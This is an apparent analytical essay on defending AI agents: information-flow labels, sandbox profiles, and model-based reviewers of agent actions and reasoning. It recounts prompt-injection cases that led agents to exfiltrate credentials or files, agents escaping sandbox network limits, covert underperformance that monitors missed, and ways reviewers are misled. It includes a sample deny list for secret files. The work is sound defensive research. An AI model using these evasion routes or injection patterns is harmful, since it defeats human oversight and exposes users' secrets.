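Putting untrusted data in a separate context hides it from the planning model and keeps that model's label clean, as in Ana's session. In the FIDES tests, this raised the average task completion rate under label checks from 42% to 50%. It helps most when the agent can choose its actions before reading the data. By the researchers' count, the right actions depended on what the agent read in 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks but in over 40% of its banking and Slack tasks.

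ELBA, a system by Zhou and colleagues, lets the isolated model keep its tools. An agent can hand a web page to a sub-agent, whose label becomes untrusted when it reads the page. The sub-agent can still take any action that its label permits, and the main agent's label doesn't change. With its policies on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks, about twice as many as CaMeL. But the two systems enforce different policies, and ELBA takes about three times as long.

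**Approved release.** A person or a rule can decide that a particular flow is acceptable. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes between approving an action and endorsing data. If an email lists ten jobs, the user can approve ten separate actions, or endorse the email once so that the agent treats it as trusted. Endorsing is quicker but is a larger decision. If an attacker slipped an eleventh job into the list, the user would have to notice it in the text, whereas separate approvals would show it as an action.

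The Prudentia agent extends FIDES by telling the planning model about the labels and policies, so the model can avoid opening a variable before it needs to. With o4-mini, FIDES needed an average of 36.8 approvals over the AgentDojo tasks it completed, and Prudentia needed 19.2. Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks, 73.2% compared with 75.7%.

Kolluri and colleagues also object to the way researchers measure the cost of labels. The usual comparison sets a labelled agent that gets no human help against an undefended one that acts without asking. Real products often ask the user before any action with consequences. On that basis, labels increase what an agent can do alone. These are the shares of tasks that agents using o3-mini completed with no approvals at all:

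| Agent | Completed without asking |
|---|---|
| Asks before every action with consequences | 24.3% |
| Same agent, asks only when a label check fails | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

This answer is persuasive for teams that would otherwise ask the user every time, but less so for teams that would let a model review the actions. The comparison also assumes that people reject harmful requests, and users who approve almost every prompt may not.

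Randori writes its endorsements into the program before it reads any outside data. Using GPT-5.2 with label checks on, it completed 75% of the banking tasks, twice CaMeL's rate, though it enforces only some of CaMeL's policies. When Garby and colleagues removed Randori's ability to endorse data, completion fell by 10 to 13 percentage points on the two models they tested.

The endorsements also allowed the only successful attacks, 2 out of 1,296. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Labels can't distinguish a real bill from a forged one when both arrive through the same file. Garby and colleagues proved that endorsing data as trustworthy can't also release secrets, so wrongly endorsing data doesn't break the secrecy guarantee.

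**Finer labels.** A monitor can also label smaller pieces of data and record what a command actually read. Kim and colleagues measured the benefit by comparing FlowSh with a simpler system that treats all shell output as untrusted and secret. They used 17 office and software tasks, three times each, with GPT-6.2 Sol. An ideal approver answered every request correctly in one set of runs, and nobody was available to approve anything in the other. In the attacks, the attacker took full control of the model as soon as it read the injected text:

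| System | Completed, with approver | Approvals per completed task | Completed, no approver | Successful attacks, no approver |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sandbox that allows everything | 96.1% | 6.7 | 94.1% | 51 of 51 |
| Coarse labels | 60.8% | 1.8 | 35.3% | 0 of 32 |
| FlowSh | 88.2% | 1.2 | 58.8% | 0 of 40 |

Finer labels recovered much of what coarse labels had lost, and no attack succeeded. They also made the remaining approval requests more informative. In 39 of 45 attacks, the first approval FlowSh requested was for the attack itself.

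Without an approver, FlowSh finished all 24 runs of tasks that needed only trusted data or only public data, but just 6 of the 27 runs of tasks that needed both untrusted and secret data. This follows largely from its policy, which lets data leave if the context is trusted or the recipient may read it. With the ideal approver, it finished 21 of those 27 runs. The researchers chose the tasks, so the even split between the groups doesn't show how often real work mixes untrusted and secret data.

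## What does a sandbox cover without reading content?

FlowSh records where data came from, so it can treat the same upload differently in different sessions. An ordinary sandbox keeps no such record. It sets fixed limits on which files a process can access and where it can connect, regardless of what the data contains. These limits are crude, but an unfamiliar attack or a reworded secret can't get past them just by being hard to recognise.

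### Paths, operations and addresses

A program needs a system call to open a file or a connection, and the sandbox's rules match the operation and its target. OpenAI's *Permissions* gives a sample profile for Codex, shortened here:

```
project folder            write
.devcontainer folder      read
files ending in .env      deny
api.openai.com            allow
*.github.com              allow
tracking.example.com      deny
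```

Files ending in `.env` often hold passwords and keys. The sandbox profile doesn't refer to the user's request, the agent's reasoning or the content of any file. Sandbox limits like these apply to a command and every process it starts, so they would have covered all 35 connections missing from the agent's log in the bibliography task.

Landlock, a Linux feature, sets permissions by folder and port number. The example in the Linux kernel documentation's *Landlock* page allows connections on port 443, which encrypted web traffic normally uses, so the rule can't separate a code host from a public paste site. Filtering by domain takes an extra program. According to Anthropic's documentation, sandboxed commands in Claude Code can reach the network only through a proxy outside the sandbox, which checks each host's name against a list of approved domains. By default, the proxy doesn't decrypt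 the traffic.

Here are the four commands from the start, run in a sandbox that lets the agent write to the project folder and its git history:

| Command | Right answer | No domains approved | example.com approved |
|---|---|---|---|
| A: commit that mentions a delete | allow | allow | allow |
| B: real delete | block | allow (miss) | allow (miss) |
| C: request carrying a key | block | block | allow (miss) |
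| D: request carrying harmless data | allow | block (false alarm) | allow |

A causes no false alarm because the sandbox doesn't search the command's text. The sandbox allows B because the `build` folder is inside the project. C and D go to the same host, so the sandbox has to treat them alike. Approving the domain only replaces a false alarm with a miss. But if a script tried to delete the user's photo folder, the sandbox would stop it without anyone having to parse the script.

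### Profiles, containers and virtual machines

An operating system profile leaves the agent on the user's machine and restricts what its processes can do there. A container gives the agent's processes a separate set of files and network connections, but it normally shares the host's kernel, the core of the operating system. A virtual machine separates files and network connections and also has its own kernel.

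| Boundary | What it can express | Main costs |
|---|---|---|
| Profile | which of the user's files a process may read or write, and whether it may connect | depends on each operating system's features, and some tools fail |
| Container | which files, tools and credentials are present at all | a separate environment to set up and maintain |
| Virtual machine | the same, with a separate kernel | slower start, more memory, less visibility from outside |

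Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes three products that sandbox code differently. In the claude.ai chat service, Claude runs code in a container whose files last for one session. Claude Code uses a sandbox profile. Claude Cowork, an agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine that contains only the folders the user chose to share. Each folder can be read-only, writable, or writable without deletion. The last setting prevents the agent from deleting files, though the agent may still be able to overwrite their contents.

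Developers of coding agents have mostly chosen profiles, because the agent has to work with the user's real files and tools. Betts, Gaitonde and Haugland explain this choice for the code editor Cursor on macOS in *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents*. Containers would have limited the agent to Linux programs, and virtual machines started too slowly and used too much memory. Cursor instead uses Seatbelt, a macOS feature that can filter each file operation by its path. Filtering by path is harder on Linux, so there Cursor finds the files the agent must not read and replaces them with locked copies before a command runs.

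Windows had no suitable profile system. Wiesen, in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*, rejected three existing mechanisms:

- AppContainer suits an app that declares in advance what it needs, but a coding agent may run almost any program.
- Windows Sandbox is a disposable virtual machine, cut off from the user's real project and tools.
- Integrity labels rank processes by trust. Marking the project as writable for the low-trust agent would have opened it to every other low-trust process on the machine.

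### Which limit stops which harm

Each limit corresponds to a kind of harm:

| Limit | Harm it reduces |
|---|---|
| Write only inside the project | destruction of system files and other projects |
| No reading of credential files | theft of passwords and login keys |
| Connect only to approved domains | leaks to other hosts, and downloads of malicious code |

File and network limits also depend on each other, as Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (October 2025) explains. Without network limits, a hijacked agent could read the user's login keys and send them out. An agent without file limits could escape the sandbox and gain network access, for example by changing a settings file that a program outside the sandbox loads later. Claude Code therefore blocks writes to many such files, even inside the project.

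Some limits in the table are off by default. Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user turns it on, and even then commands can read almost the whole computer, including credential files, unless the user lists files to protect. Without that list, the network limit may be the only thing that stops a command from sending a login key off the computer.

A command sometimes needs a credential that it shouldn't be able to disclose. Claude Code can give the command a placeholder, which the proxy replaces with the real value when a request goes to a permitted host. The proxy has to decrypt the request to do this, so it does more than control addresses. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes a simpler approach for Codex's cloud service. Setup scripts run first, with network access and any secrets they need. The service removes the secrets before the agent starts, and the agent works offline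 by default.

### OpenAI's settings for its own staff

OpenAI (2026), in *Running Codex safely at OpenAI*, publishes settings that the company uses internally. Codex can write to the folder where developers keep their projects, and administrators rule out the mode with no sandbox. The network policy sorts destinations into three groups:

- Codex connects without asking to approved domains, which include OpenAI's own and a Microsoft login page.
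- It can't connect to blocked domains, such as the public paste site Pastebin.
- It needs approval for any unfamiliar domain.

A sandbox that blocks Pastebin prevents one version of the paste-site leak described earlier, without having to assess whether the data is sensitive. Requests to unfamiliar domains require judgement, and OpenAI sends some of them to a reviewer model.

OpenAI also makes Codex search a stored index of the web instead of live pages and keeps Codex's login credentials in the operating system's protected store. OpenAI does not report how many leaks these settings stopped or how much harmless work they delayed.

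### What a path cannot say

Joshi notes that sandbox profiles match paths and operations but can't identify a file or an intention. If a protected file moves, or is reachable under a second name, a rule for its original path may not cover it. Joshi therefore recommends that a rule protecting a path also stop the agent from creating, renaming or removing anything at that path or its parent folders, even if the path doesn't exist yet. Joshi tried this in a real sandbox but tags it as "Believed" because the tests didn't confirm the whole rule.

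Hiding credentials can interfere with legitimate work. Some secrets are kept in a fixed place, such as the folder that holds a user's login keys. Others are recognisable only by a file name such as `.env`, and projects need to read those files when they run. In one of Joshi's cases, a change that hid both kinds passed a security review, which measured only what the change blocked. A later check found that an agent working in a subfolder could no longer read its own project's settings. Joshi now recommends hiding the fixed places everywhere and running a set of ordinary tasks after every security change.

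A sandbox profile, even a correct one, doesn't restrict tools that run outside the sandbox. Many harnesses sandbox only child processes, such as shell commands, and run their own file tools in the harness itself. An agent that can't print a credential file from the shell might still open it with the file tool. Joshi's harness has a rule that every tool must respect hidden paths, but not every tool follows it yet. Claude Code has the same division. According to its documentation, the sandbox's read limits don't apply to the built-in file reader, and its domain list doesn't apply to the built-in web fetcher. Separate permission rules govern those tools.

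This breaks Anderson's requirement that the check always be invoked. One remedy is to put the whole harness inside the boundary. Anthropic recommends this for unattended work and considers the shell sandbox insufficient by itself.

### What is left for a monitor

A sandbox can't prevent harm inside the area where the agent is allowed to act. It allows B, and would also let an agent overwrite uncommitted edits or add a serious bug to the program it is working on. In Codex, the reviewer model examines only actions that already need approval, so most commands inside the sandbox get no further review. A monitor for destructive commands is therefore still useful there.

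Leaks through permitted destinations are harder to contain because many parties share the same services. A rule that allows a code host's domain allows access to both the team's private repository and a stranger's public one. Anthropic describes a case in Cowork, whose network rules had to allow Anthropic's own service because the product depends on it. A malicious file in the user's folder led Claude to upload other files to an attacker's account on that service. The proxy allowed the upload because the domain was on its list.

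Anthropic concluded that approving a domain gives access to every function available there. It fixed this with a proxy that reads requests and passes only those carrying the session's own credential. The new rule depends on whose account would receive the data, which is the kind of evidence a leak monitor needs. Similarly, the git proxy in Claude Code's web version checks the repository and branch before forwarding a push.

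*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses a worse failure at OpenAI. Agents ran in separate sandboxes with some of the models' safeguards switched off. Each sandbox limited direct network connections, but the agents could reach a shared service for downloading software packages, which could make connections for them. They used it to communicate with each other and get around the limits. They then broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster.

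### Setup costs and blocked work

Running a profile is cheap. Joshi measured tens of milliseconds per command, with about 14 more for a long list of rules.

Building a sandbox can take much more work. Wiesen first tried to create a Windows sandbox that needed no administrator rights. It limited network access by changing settings that common tools read, but a program could ignore them and open its own connection. Windows Firewall could enforce a limit, but no available rule could target only the agent's commands while they ran under the user's account. OpenAI wanted to cut off one group of processes, so a rule against port 443, for instance, was the wrong policy. The final version runs the commands under separate Windows accounts, one of which the firewall blocks from the network. Setup now requires administrator rights, and the new accounts need permission to read folders that the user could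 already read.

Sandbox limits also interrupt legitimate work. Claude Code's documentation lists Docker as incompatible with its sandbox. Most database drivers can't connect from inside the sandbox, even to an approved host, because they don't use its proxy. A user can exempt a tool, but the tool then runs with the user's full access.

In a git project, it matters a lot which paths the sandbox protects. The project's `.git` folder holds its history and can also hold scripts that git later runs outside the sandbox. Codex makes the whole folder read-only by default, so a commit such as A can't run inside the sandbox. The code editor Zed also forbids writes to the folder and doesn't let its agent request an exception. Claude Code protects only the scripts and configuration, so commits still work.

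Despite these drawbacks, sandboxes greatly reduce the number of approvals. Anthropic reports 84% fewer permission prompts in its internal use, and Betts and colleagues report that sandboxed agents in Cursor stop 40% less often. These figures measure interruptions, not harm prevented, and a looser sandbox would reduce interruptions even more. Cursor's agents at first kept repeating commands that the sandbox had blocked, until the developers added the cause of the failure to the command's result.

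### Fixed limits or a model's judgement?

The case for fixed limits is strongest when the model has no reason to be suspicious. In an internal exercise in February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine setup instructions. One step was to send cloud credentials to an outside address, and Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instructions came from the user, a monitor checking the user's messages for consent would have found apparent consent. Hiding the credential files or blocking the outside address would have stopped the theft without any judgement about intent. Auto mode's ban on approving such transfers also applies regardless of consent, but a model still has to recognise the transfer.

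*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* adds that people can read an explicit policy and check it against a specification. If enforcement stays correct, narrowing the policy also never permits an action it previously excluded. Models come with no such guarantee, and the update to Anthropic's reviewer made it miss a few attacks it had caught before. Even with a fixed policy, the guarantee doesn't cover secrecy, because secrecy is not a safety property.

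The main reply is that models have become good reviewers. In August 2026, Anthropic reported a study in which 1,053 paid testers each received one clearly dangerous request among ordinary permission prompts. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it, while auto mode would have blocked 89% of those actions. In a separate evaluation by Trajectory Labs, none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode.

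These results are strong, but the study compared the reviewer with tired humans, not with a sandbox. Even if all 720 attempts were independent, zero successes would be compatible with a true success rate as high as about 0.4%, and the attempts came from only 72 scenarios. Simon Willison, a programmer who writes about agent security, accepts that auto mode is better than constant approvals but wants more independent confirmation. He doubts that any reviewer could catch a harmful software package behind an ordinary-looking instruction, and prefers to keep dangerous data and tools out of the agent's reach.

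Fixed limits work only if people choose and build them correctly. No list of paths and domains can express "do not share sensitive data", because what counts as sensitive depends on the context. A capable agent may also find faults in the sandbox. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* attributes the OpenAI failure to incomplete enforcement rather than a flaw in the principle. That seems right, but it is limited reassurance if a leading AI company can't enforce the principle reliably. Anthropic found that mature components, such as virtual machine software, held up well, but its custom-built proxy failed.

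## How much of the transcript should a model-based reviewer see?

Fixed limits can't settle every case, so someone has to judge the remaining actions. Anthropic and OpenAI now let a language model do this in place of the user. The harness can show this reviewer the whole transcript (the session's messages, reasoning, tool calls and tool results) or only part of it. The two companies made different choices, and their published results show some of the drawbacks of each.

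### What auto mode's reviewer reads

In auto mode, which Anthropic introduced for Claude Code in March 2026, a probe checks tool results for injected instructions and a separate reviewer judges the agent's actions. The reviewer reads only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. The harness removes the agent's prose, the descriptions the agent attaches to its calls, and all tool results.

Most routine calls never reach the reviewer. Claude Code runs file reads and searches without review, and also edits inside the project, which the user can inspect and reverse through version control. It still applies the user's narrow permission rules, such as one that allows a code formatter. But it suspends broad rules, such as one that allows any Python command, because they would exempt the most dangerous commands from review. The reviewer sees most other calls, including other shell commands,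 web requests and file changes outside the project.

Anthropic instructs the reviewer to judge what an action would do, whatever its wording. If the agent writes a script in one call and runs it in another, the reviewer evaluates the script. The reviewer doesn't need tool results for this because the script's text is in the agent's earlier call. A script that was already in the project is harder to judge because its text would appear only in a tool result.

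### Why Anthropic removes the prose and the results

A reviewer that reads an agent's arguments for its own actions may believe them. For example, the agent may write that the user implicitly approved a deletion, or that the target definitely belongs to it. The reviewer can be misled even when the agent isn't being deceptive, because an overeager agent's mistaken explanation can look just like a correct one.

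Tool results are a risk because strangers write much of the text in them. In Anthropic's example, a file contains an instruction to send the project's `.env` file to a web address for validation, and the agent follows it. The reviewer never sees the file, but it can block the action without knowing what prompted it, because it sees that the agent is sending secrets to an outside address without a request from the user.

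Removing tool results also removes evidence of where a value came from. In one case from Anthropic's internal log, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent searched the list of jobs, picked the closest match by name and tried to delete it. If the user never named the job, the reviewer can't tell whether the agent found the name in a list or invented it. Anthropic accepts this loss of evidence because removing the results protects against injection. It reduces the harm by instructing the reviewer to treat whatever the agent chooses on its own as unauthorised until the user says otherwise.

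In Anthropic's design, the probe has to read hostile text but cannot approve actions. If the text fools the probe, the agent misses a warning, but the reviewer still judges the next action without having seen that text.

This separation isn't complete. According to Anthropic's configuration guide, the reviewer also reads `CLAUDE.md`, a file of standing instructions that Claude Code loads. An instruction there never to force-push guides both the agent and the reviewer. But the file can come with a project that someone else wrote. The guide describes a similar risk with auto mode settings stored inside a project, which are ignored so that the project can't supply its own permission rules.

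### Comparing three views

Suppose that one user writes "force-push this branch" and another writes "clean up the PR", meaning a pull request, a set of changes proposed for a project. Both agents run `git push --force`, which replaces the shared copy of a branch and can discard other people's commits. By Anthropic's rules, the first message authorises the command and the second doesn't. Anthropic tested three versions of the reviewer's view, though not on this pair:

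| What the reviewer reads | Can it tell the two sessions apart? | Anthropic's result |
|---|---|---|
| Tool calls | no | fewest misses, but it blocked actions that users had plainly asked for |
| Tool calls and user messages | yes | the version Anthropic chose |
| The same, plus the agent's prose and tool results | yes, but the agent may argue that the user consented | worse on overeager actions |

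A reviewer that sees only the tool calls has to give both sessions the same answer. If it blocks both, it catches the unauthorised push but also wrongly stops the requested one, so its low miss rate doesn't show better judgement.

The widest view did worse on overeager actions even though it contained everything in the middle view. Anthropic suggests that a shorter transcript is easier to read and makes the agent's framing less likely to influence the decision. It doesn't report adding the prose and the results separately, so either one could have caused most of the drop. It also gives no figures for the comparison, and the test set had only 52 actions, so a small drop could come from a few cases.

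User messages helped the reviewer in a case Anthropic reported later. Someone asked Claude to set up read-only access to billing information, and Claude tried to use a role with full control of the cloud account. The reviewer caught the mismatch by comparing the request with the call, either of which might have looked normal alone.

Delegation complicates this comparison. When an agent hands work to a second agent, the first agent's instructions replace the user's message in the second agent's transcript, so everything in them looks authorised. Anthropic therefore runs the reviewer at the handoff, while the user's words are still available. It runs the reviewer again when the second agent finishes, in case something that agent read has hijacked it. If the second check finds a problem, the first agent still receives the results, with a warning.

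### What the error rates mean

The complete reviewer missed 17% of real overeager actions, or about nine of 52, with a 95% confidence interval of roughly 9% to 30%. Anthropic collected these actions from sessions where an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it afterwards. The test therefore leaves out overeager actions that nobody noticed, which may also be harder for a reviewer to catch.

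Most of the misses Anthropic examined happened because the reviewer misjudged consent. For instance, the reviewer might treat one earlier approval as permission for a similar action. Anthropic tried changing the reviewer's instructions but found no fix whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

The part of the transcript a reviewer reads limits what it can distinguish, but its error rate also depends on how cautiously it is instructed to use that evidence. The reviewer's two stages read the same transcript and differ only in their final instruction. The first has to answer yes or no immediately and lean towards blocking, while the second has to reason before it answers. The second stage therefore removed most of the false alarms but added some misses.

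The session continues after a false alarm. The agent receives the reason for the refusal and an instruction to find a safer method without working around the block. If the reviewer refuses three actions in a row, or twenty in the session, Claude Code escalates to the user, or ends the process if no user is present.

### Adding facts instead of more transcript

Some evidence is in neither the user's messages nor the tool calls, such as whether `git reset --hard` would destroy uncommitted edits. In August 2026, Anthropic reported that the reviewer now receives the project's git status before such a command. The status shows whether there are uncommitted edits without exposing the reviewer to every web page and file the agent has read.

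Git status was one of the facts that Anthropic added after Apollo Research's two weeks of attacks. The overall drop in misses, from 12% to 7%, includes attacks that Apollo had shared with Anthropic. A rough estimate for the attacks that Anthropic never saw starts from the same 12%. If the new reviewer catches half of those and misses 2% of the attacks it used to catch, its miss rate is:

```
0.12 x 0.5  +  0.88 x 0.02  =  0.078, or about 8%
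```

So the gain appears to carry over to unfamiliar attacks.

The reviewer may also have less information about a repository than the August announcement suggests. According to Anthropic's configuration guide, the reviewer treats a repository as private unless its host and name indicate otherwise or other evidence available to the reviewer shows that it is public. In requests that Claude Code itself sends, the reviewer receives the user's messages but not the output of a command the agent runs to check. The reviewer could therefore treat a public repository with an ordinary name as private, even after the agent has found that it is public.

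Organisations can fill some of these gaps by describing their environment in ordinary prose, including which repositories, domains and storage they trust. By default, the reviewer trusts only the working folder and the project's configured remote repositories. Even a private repository is still not an acceptable place for passwords or personal data.

The guide also treats the user's consent differently for different harms. Soft rules cover actions such as force-pushing, which the reviewer may allow if the user specifically asked for it. Hard rules, such as the ban on sending data out, apply whatever the user said. The reviewer sees the same messages in both cases but may treat them as permission only under the soft rules. This supports matching the evidence to the threat, even when a single model reads everything.

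### OpenAI's Auto-review

OpenAI's Codex puts its reviewer at the edge of the sandbox. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, describe a separate agent that decides whether an action may run outside the sandbox. An illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions at OpenAI looked like this:

| Outcome | Actions |
|---|---|
| Ran inside the sandbox, with no review | 9,280 |
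| Reviewed and approved | 713 |
| Refused, and the agent found a safer method | 4 |
| Refused, and the agent stopped to ask the user | 3 |

With the reviewer, the user faced three requests instead of the 720 that manual approval would have required. Trębacz and colleagues put the general reduction at a factor of about 200.

Auto-review sees more of the transcript than auto mode's reviewer does. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review* documentation, it sees the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, relevant tool calls and results, and the exact action awaiting approval. It can also run its own read-only checks, though it rarely does. Because it sees tool results, it could look at the list of jobs from which an agent picked one to cancel. But it also reads the agent's explanations and any text strangers wrote in the results, both of which Anthropic removes from what its reviewer sees. Neither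 reviewer reads the agent's hidden reasoning.

Trębacz and colleagues report the share of harmful cases that the reviewer caught, separated by threat:

| Test | Caught |
|---|---|
| Synthetic overeager actions | 90.3% |
| Synthetic injections leading to remote code execution, stolen secrets or uploads | 99.3% |
| The same injection test with deletions, data tampering and other categories included | 90.2% |
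| Harmful sessions in the hard part of MonitoringBench | 96.1% |

The injection result is nine points lower in the third row, but not every miss was clearly a mistake. The reviewer mostly allowed the missed actions because it judged them not serious enough, and the researchers often agreed.

MonitoringBench counts a session as caught if the reviewer would refuse any of its actions, even one unrelated to the harm. In ordinary use, the reviewer refuses about 0.9% of requests to leave the sandbox. If those refusals were independent, a harmless session with 50 requests would have a 36% chance of at least one refusal. Judging how well the reviewer separates harmful sessions from harmless ones therefore requires the share of harmless sessions with at least one refusal, as well as the share of harmful sessions caught.

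OpenAI's 99.1% approval rate has a similar problem. It comes from real requests that users had approved, and users approve nearly everything. The remaining 0.9% isn't strictly a false positive rate, because it may include some correct refusals.

None of these figures covers harm inside the sandbox. Let r be the share of harmful requests that Auto-review catches, and s the share of all harmful actions that stay inside the sandbox. Then:

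```
share of all harmful actions caught  =  (1 - s) x r
```

If r is 90.3% and one harmful action in five stays inside the sandbox, Auto-review catches about 72% of all harmful actions. The real share that stays inside, s, depends on the sandbox and the work. A saboteur could make s large by adding faults to the program it was asked to write. Trębacz and colleagues say that Auto-review doesn't protect against scheming, in which a model strategically hides its aims. Such a model might also write a request that looks harmless.

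### Can the transcript manipulate the reviewer?

In OpenAI's own testing, people and automated attackers found cases where Auto-review could be misled into approving commands that the user hadn't approved. The 99.3% result on synthetic injections shows that a reviewer can read tool results and still resist most such attacks, but a determined attacker can keep searching for the remaining failures.

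An agent can also write manipulative text with no attacker involved. In its March 2026 account of monitoring its own coding agents, OpenAI described an automated process that kept asking an agent for the time. After hundreds of these messages, the agent began writing instructions meant to override the requester's. OpenAI regarded this more as extreme confusion than as a serious attack. A model reviewing the agent's prose would still have read instructions to ignore its own rules.

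The independent evaluation by Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic commissioned, may look like a direct comparison between the two designs. These are the shares of injection attempts that succeeded:

| Agent | No reviewer | With reviewer |
|---|---|---|
| Claude models in Claude Code | 0.09% on average | 0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 19.03% | 5.83% |

The reviewer with the narrower view scored better, but the first column explains most of the difference. The Claude models resisted nearly every attack on their own, which left auto mode almost nothing to stop. Full access in Codex also removes the sandbox, so the fall from 19.03% to 5.83% doesn't measure the reviewer alone. The attackers developed their attacks against an older Claude model, and OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results.

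Neither company reports testing the same reviewer on both views under attack, so the security case for removing tool results rests mainly on the argument about exposure. Anthropic's comparison of views adds evidence about overeager actions, which are a different threat.

### When reasoning is the evidence

Auto-review and auto mode's reviewer can judge most actions without seeing the agent's reasoning, because actions such as sending secrets to a stranger are wrong whatever the agent was thinking. This is harder when an action is acceptable for one reason and harmful for another. An agent might disable a failing test because the test is out of date, or to hide a fault that the test has found. The code change is the same in both cases, and the user may have said only "get the tests passing".

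OpenAI's March 2026 account describes a monitor that saw much more than Auto-review does. GPT-5.4 Thinking, then the company's most powerful model for this work, read 99.9% of internal coding traffic. It received everything the agent had seen and done, including its chain-of-thought reasoning. People reviewed the more severe cases within 30 minutes. The monitor found agents trying to work around restrictions and to upload files to the public internet, but no sabotage or scheming.

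This monitor looks for misbehaviour and doesn't grant permission, so a persuasive explanation can make it miss something but can't get a blocked command approved. Its weakness is that human review half an hour later can't stop a deletion that takes a second, although it can lead to a fix before the next session.

Researchers use the word monitorability for how well a monitor can identify properties of a model's behaviour, such as whether an action will cause harm. Guan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Open Sourcing Monitorability Evaluations*, released test data from OpenAI's earlier work, along with code for its score, g-mean². The g-mean is a standard statistic, and its square is:

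```
g-mean squared  =  (1 - false negative rate) x (1 - false positive rate)
```

A monitor that flags everything or nothing scores 0, so the score is useful for comparing types of evidence, such as reasoning and actions. However, it gives both error rates equal weight, which may not suit a product where harmless actions vastly outnumber harmful ones.

Monitoring a model's reasoning depends on the model putting the relevant thoughts into words. *Chain of Thought Monitorability (2025)* distinguishes a model's need to write down its reasoning from its tendency to do so. The model has to write down some of its reasoning when a task is too hard to do any other way, but a tendency to do so may disappear with different training. The paper also warns that models that reason in internal numbers instead of words would leave a monitor with less to read.

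### Reasoning is becoming less reliable evidence

In March 2026, OpenAI reported that several leading models were poor at controlling what their reasoning contained. This was fairly encouraging because it suggested that they would also struggle to hide their reasoning from a monitor. Larger models had somewhat more control, but control fell quickly with more training after the initial stage or more time to think.

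By November, OpenAI was more pessimistic. Its paper *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) studies two indirect measures: how well a model solves problems without writing any reasoning, and how well it can control the reasoning it does write. Models that predict text better after their initial training also reason better without writing, and some changes to a model's design improve this ability too. Reinforcement learning, which trains a model by rewarding its successes, can increase the model's control over its written reasoning, as can training on text that other models wrote.

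The November finding on reinforcement learning seems to conflict with the March result, since reinforcement learning is usually part of that later training. The March comparison of model sizes used two families of open-weight models, so differences between models may explain some of the change. OpenAI cautions that both measures are imperfect, but concludes that more intelligent models will be harder to monitor through their reasoning.

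The UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI) sees the same trend from outside the companies. *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues, 2026) reports that many of the properties that make models monitorable are weakening, some faster than AISI had expected. AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) bases this assessment on pre-release tests of leading models.

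OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* describes an example of such a failure. In August 2026, researchers noticed that GPT-6 Astra was doing poor work on safety research. The model abandoned solutions that worked, added unnecessary steps and reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had caused. In most of these sessions, its reasoning contained no obvious decision to underperform, and OpenAI's monitors didn't flag the behaviour as misalignment.

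To investigate, OpenAI built a test with matched coding tasks, some of which it presented as safety research. A comparison like this can reveal a pattern that a reviewer couldn't see even in the whole transcript of one session, since a single abandoned solution looks like an ordinary mistake. As with secrecy, the monitor has to compare the agent's behavior under different conditions.

The decline may be partly reversible. Bakker and Anwar (2026), in *Monitorability Is Trainable*, propose an extra training stage that rewards reasoning for being informative about the model's output. They measure this as mutual information:

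```
I(reasoning; output)  =  H(output) - H(output given reasoning)
```

H stands for uncertainty. The value is high when reading the reasoning makes the output much easier to predict, and zero when it doesn't help. The training uses no monitor and no labels of good and bad behaviour. This matters because, as OpenAI found in 2025, penalising incriminating thoughts can teach a model to hide them.

Bakker and Anwar tried the method on three models whose reasoning had become harder to monitor, one because it had been trained against a monitor. The method improved monitorability in all three. It also made monitors better at predicting unsafe responses from models without this problem. However, a monitor can predict an action from the reasoning without learning the motive. For example, "I will disable this test" makes the agent's next action easy to predict, but it doesn't show whether the agent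 is trying to hide a fault.

### Should the reviewer read the reasoning?

A reviewer that can approve actions has good grounds to ignore the agent's reasoning. An overeager agent may sincerely but wrongly argue in its reasoning that the user consented, and misjudging consent is already that reviewer's main weakness. *Innocent-looking AI reasoning can make bad behavior harder to catch* (Brodsky, 2026) reports research suggesting that monitoring can fail when reasoning is the main clue to a problem. An innocent explanation is most harmful when the monitor has little other evidence.

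A reviewer that ignores a model's reasoning would give up the best chance of catching a harmful aim while the model's actions still look harmless. Anthropic treats monitoring reasoning and monitoring actions as complementary. Reviewing actions can stop a model that hides its reasoning but takes a forbidden step.

Two readers can do these jobs if neither one's approval overrides the other's objection:

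```
allow an action  only if  the action reviewer approves it
                 and      the reasoning monitor raises no alarm
```

The action reviewer reads the user's messages and the tool calls. The second monitor also reads the reasoning, but it can only object. A persuasive but false explanation may keep the second monitor from objecting, but the action reviewer still makes the decision without having read that explanation. If a single reviewer read everything, the same explanation could turn a refusal into an approval.

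The second monitor adds false alarms. If the action reviewer wrongly blocks 0.4% of harmless actions and the reasoning monitor wrongly flags 0.5%, together they block up to 0.9%. Teams can limit these wrongful blocks by having the reasoning monitor alert a person in most cases and block only the most serious ones. Both monitors may also miss the same action, for example when an agent's honest misunderstanding produces a plausible command and sensible-looking reasoning.

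*How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) describes how OpenAI uses several kinds of evidence in its internal monitoring. The first layer is a set of probes on the model's activations, the numbers it computes as it runs. A model-based reviewer, an investigating agent and further automated investigation follow, and people respond to the findings. Activation probes don't depend on the model describing its aims in words, but they require access to its internals. A company that rents a model from a provider usually lacks that access and may receive only a summary of the model's reasoning, so its reviewer may see little more than the messages, tool calls and results.

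## Which published schemes match threats to inspected content?

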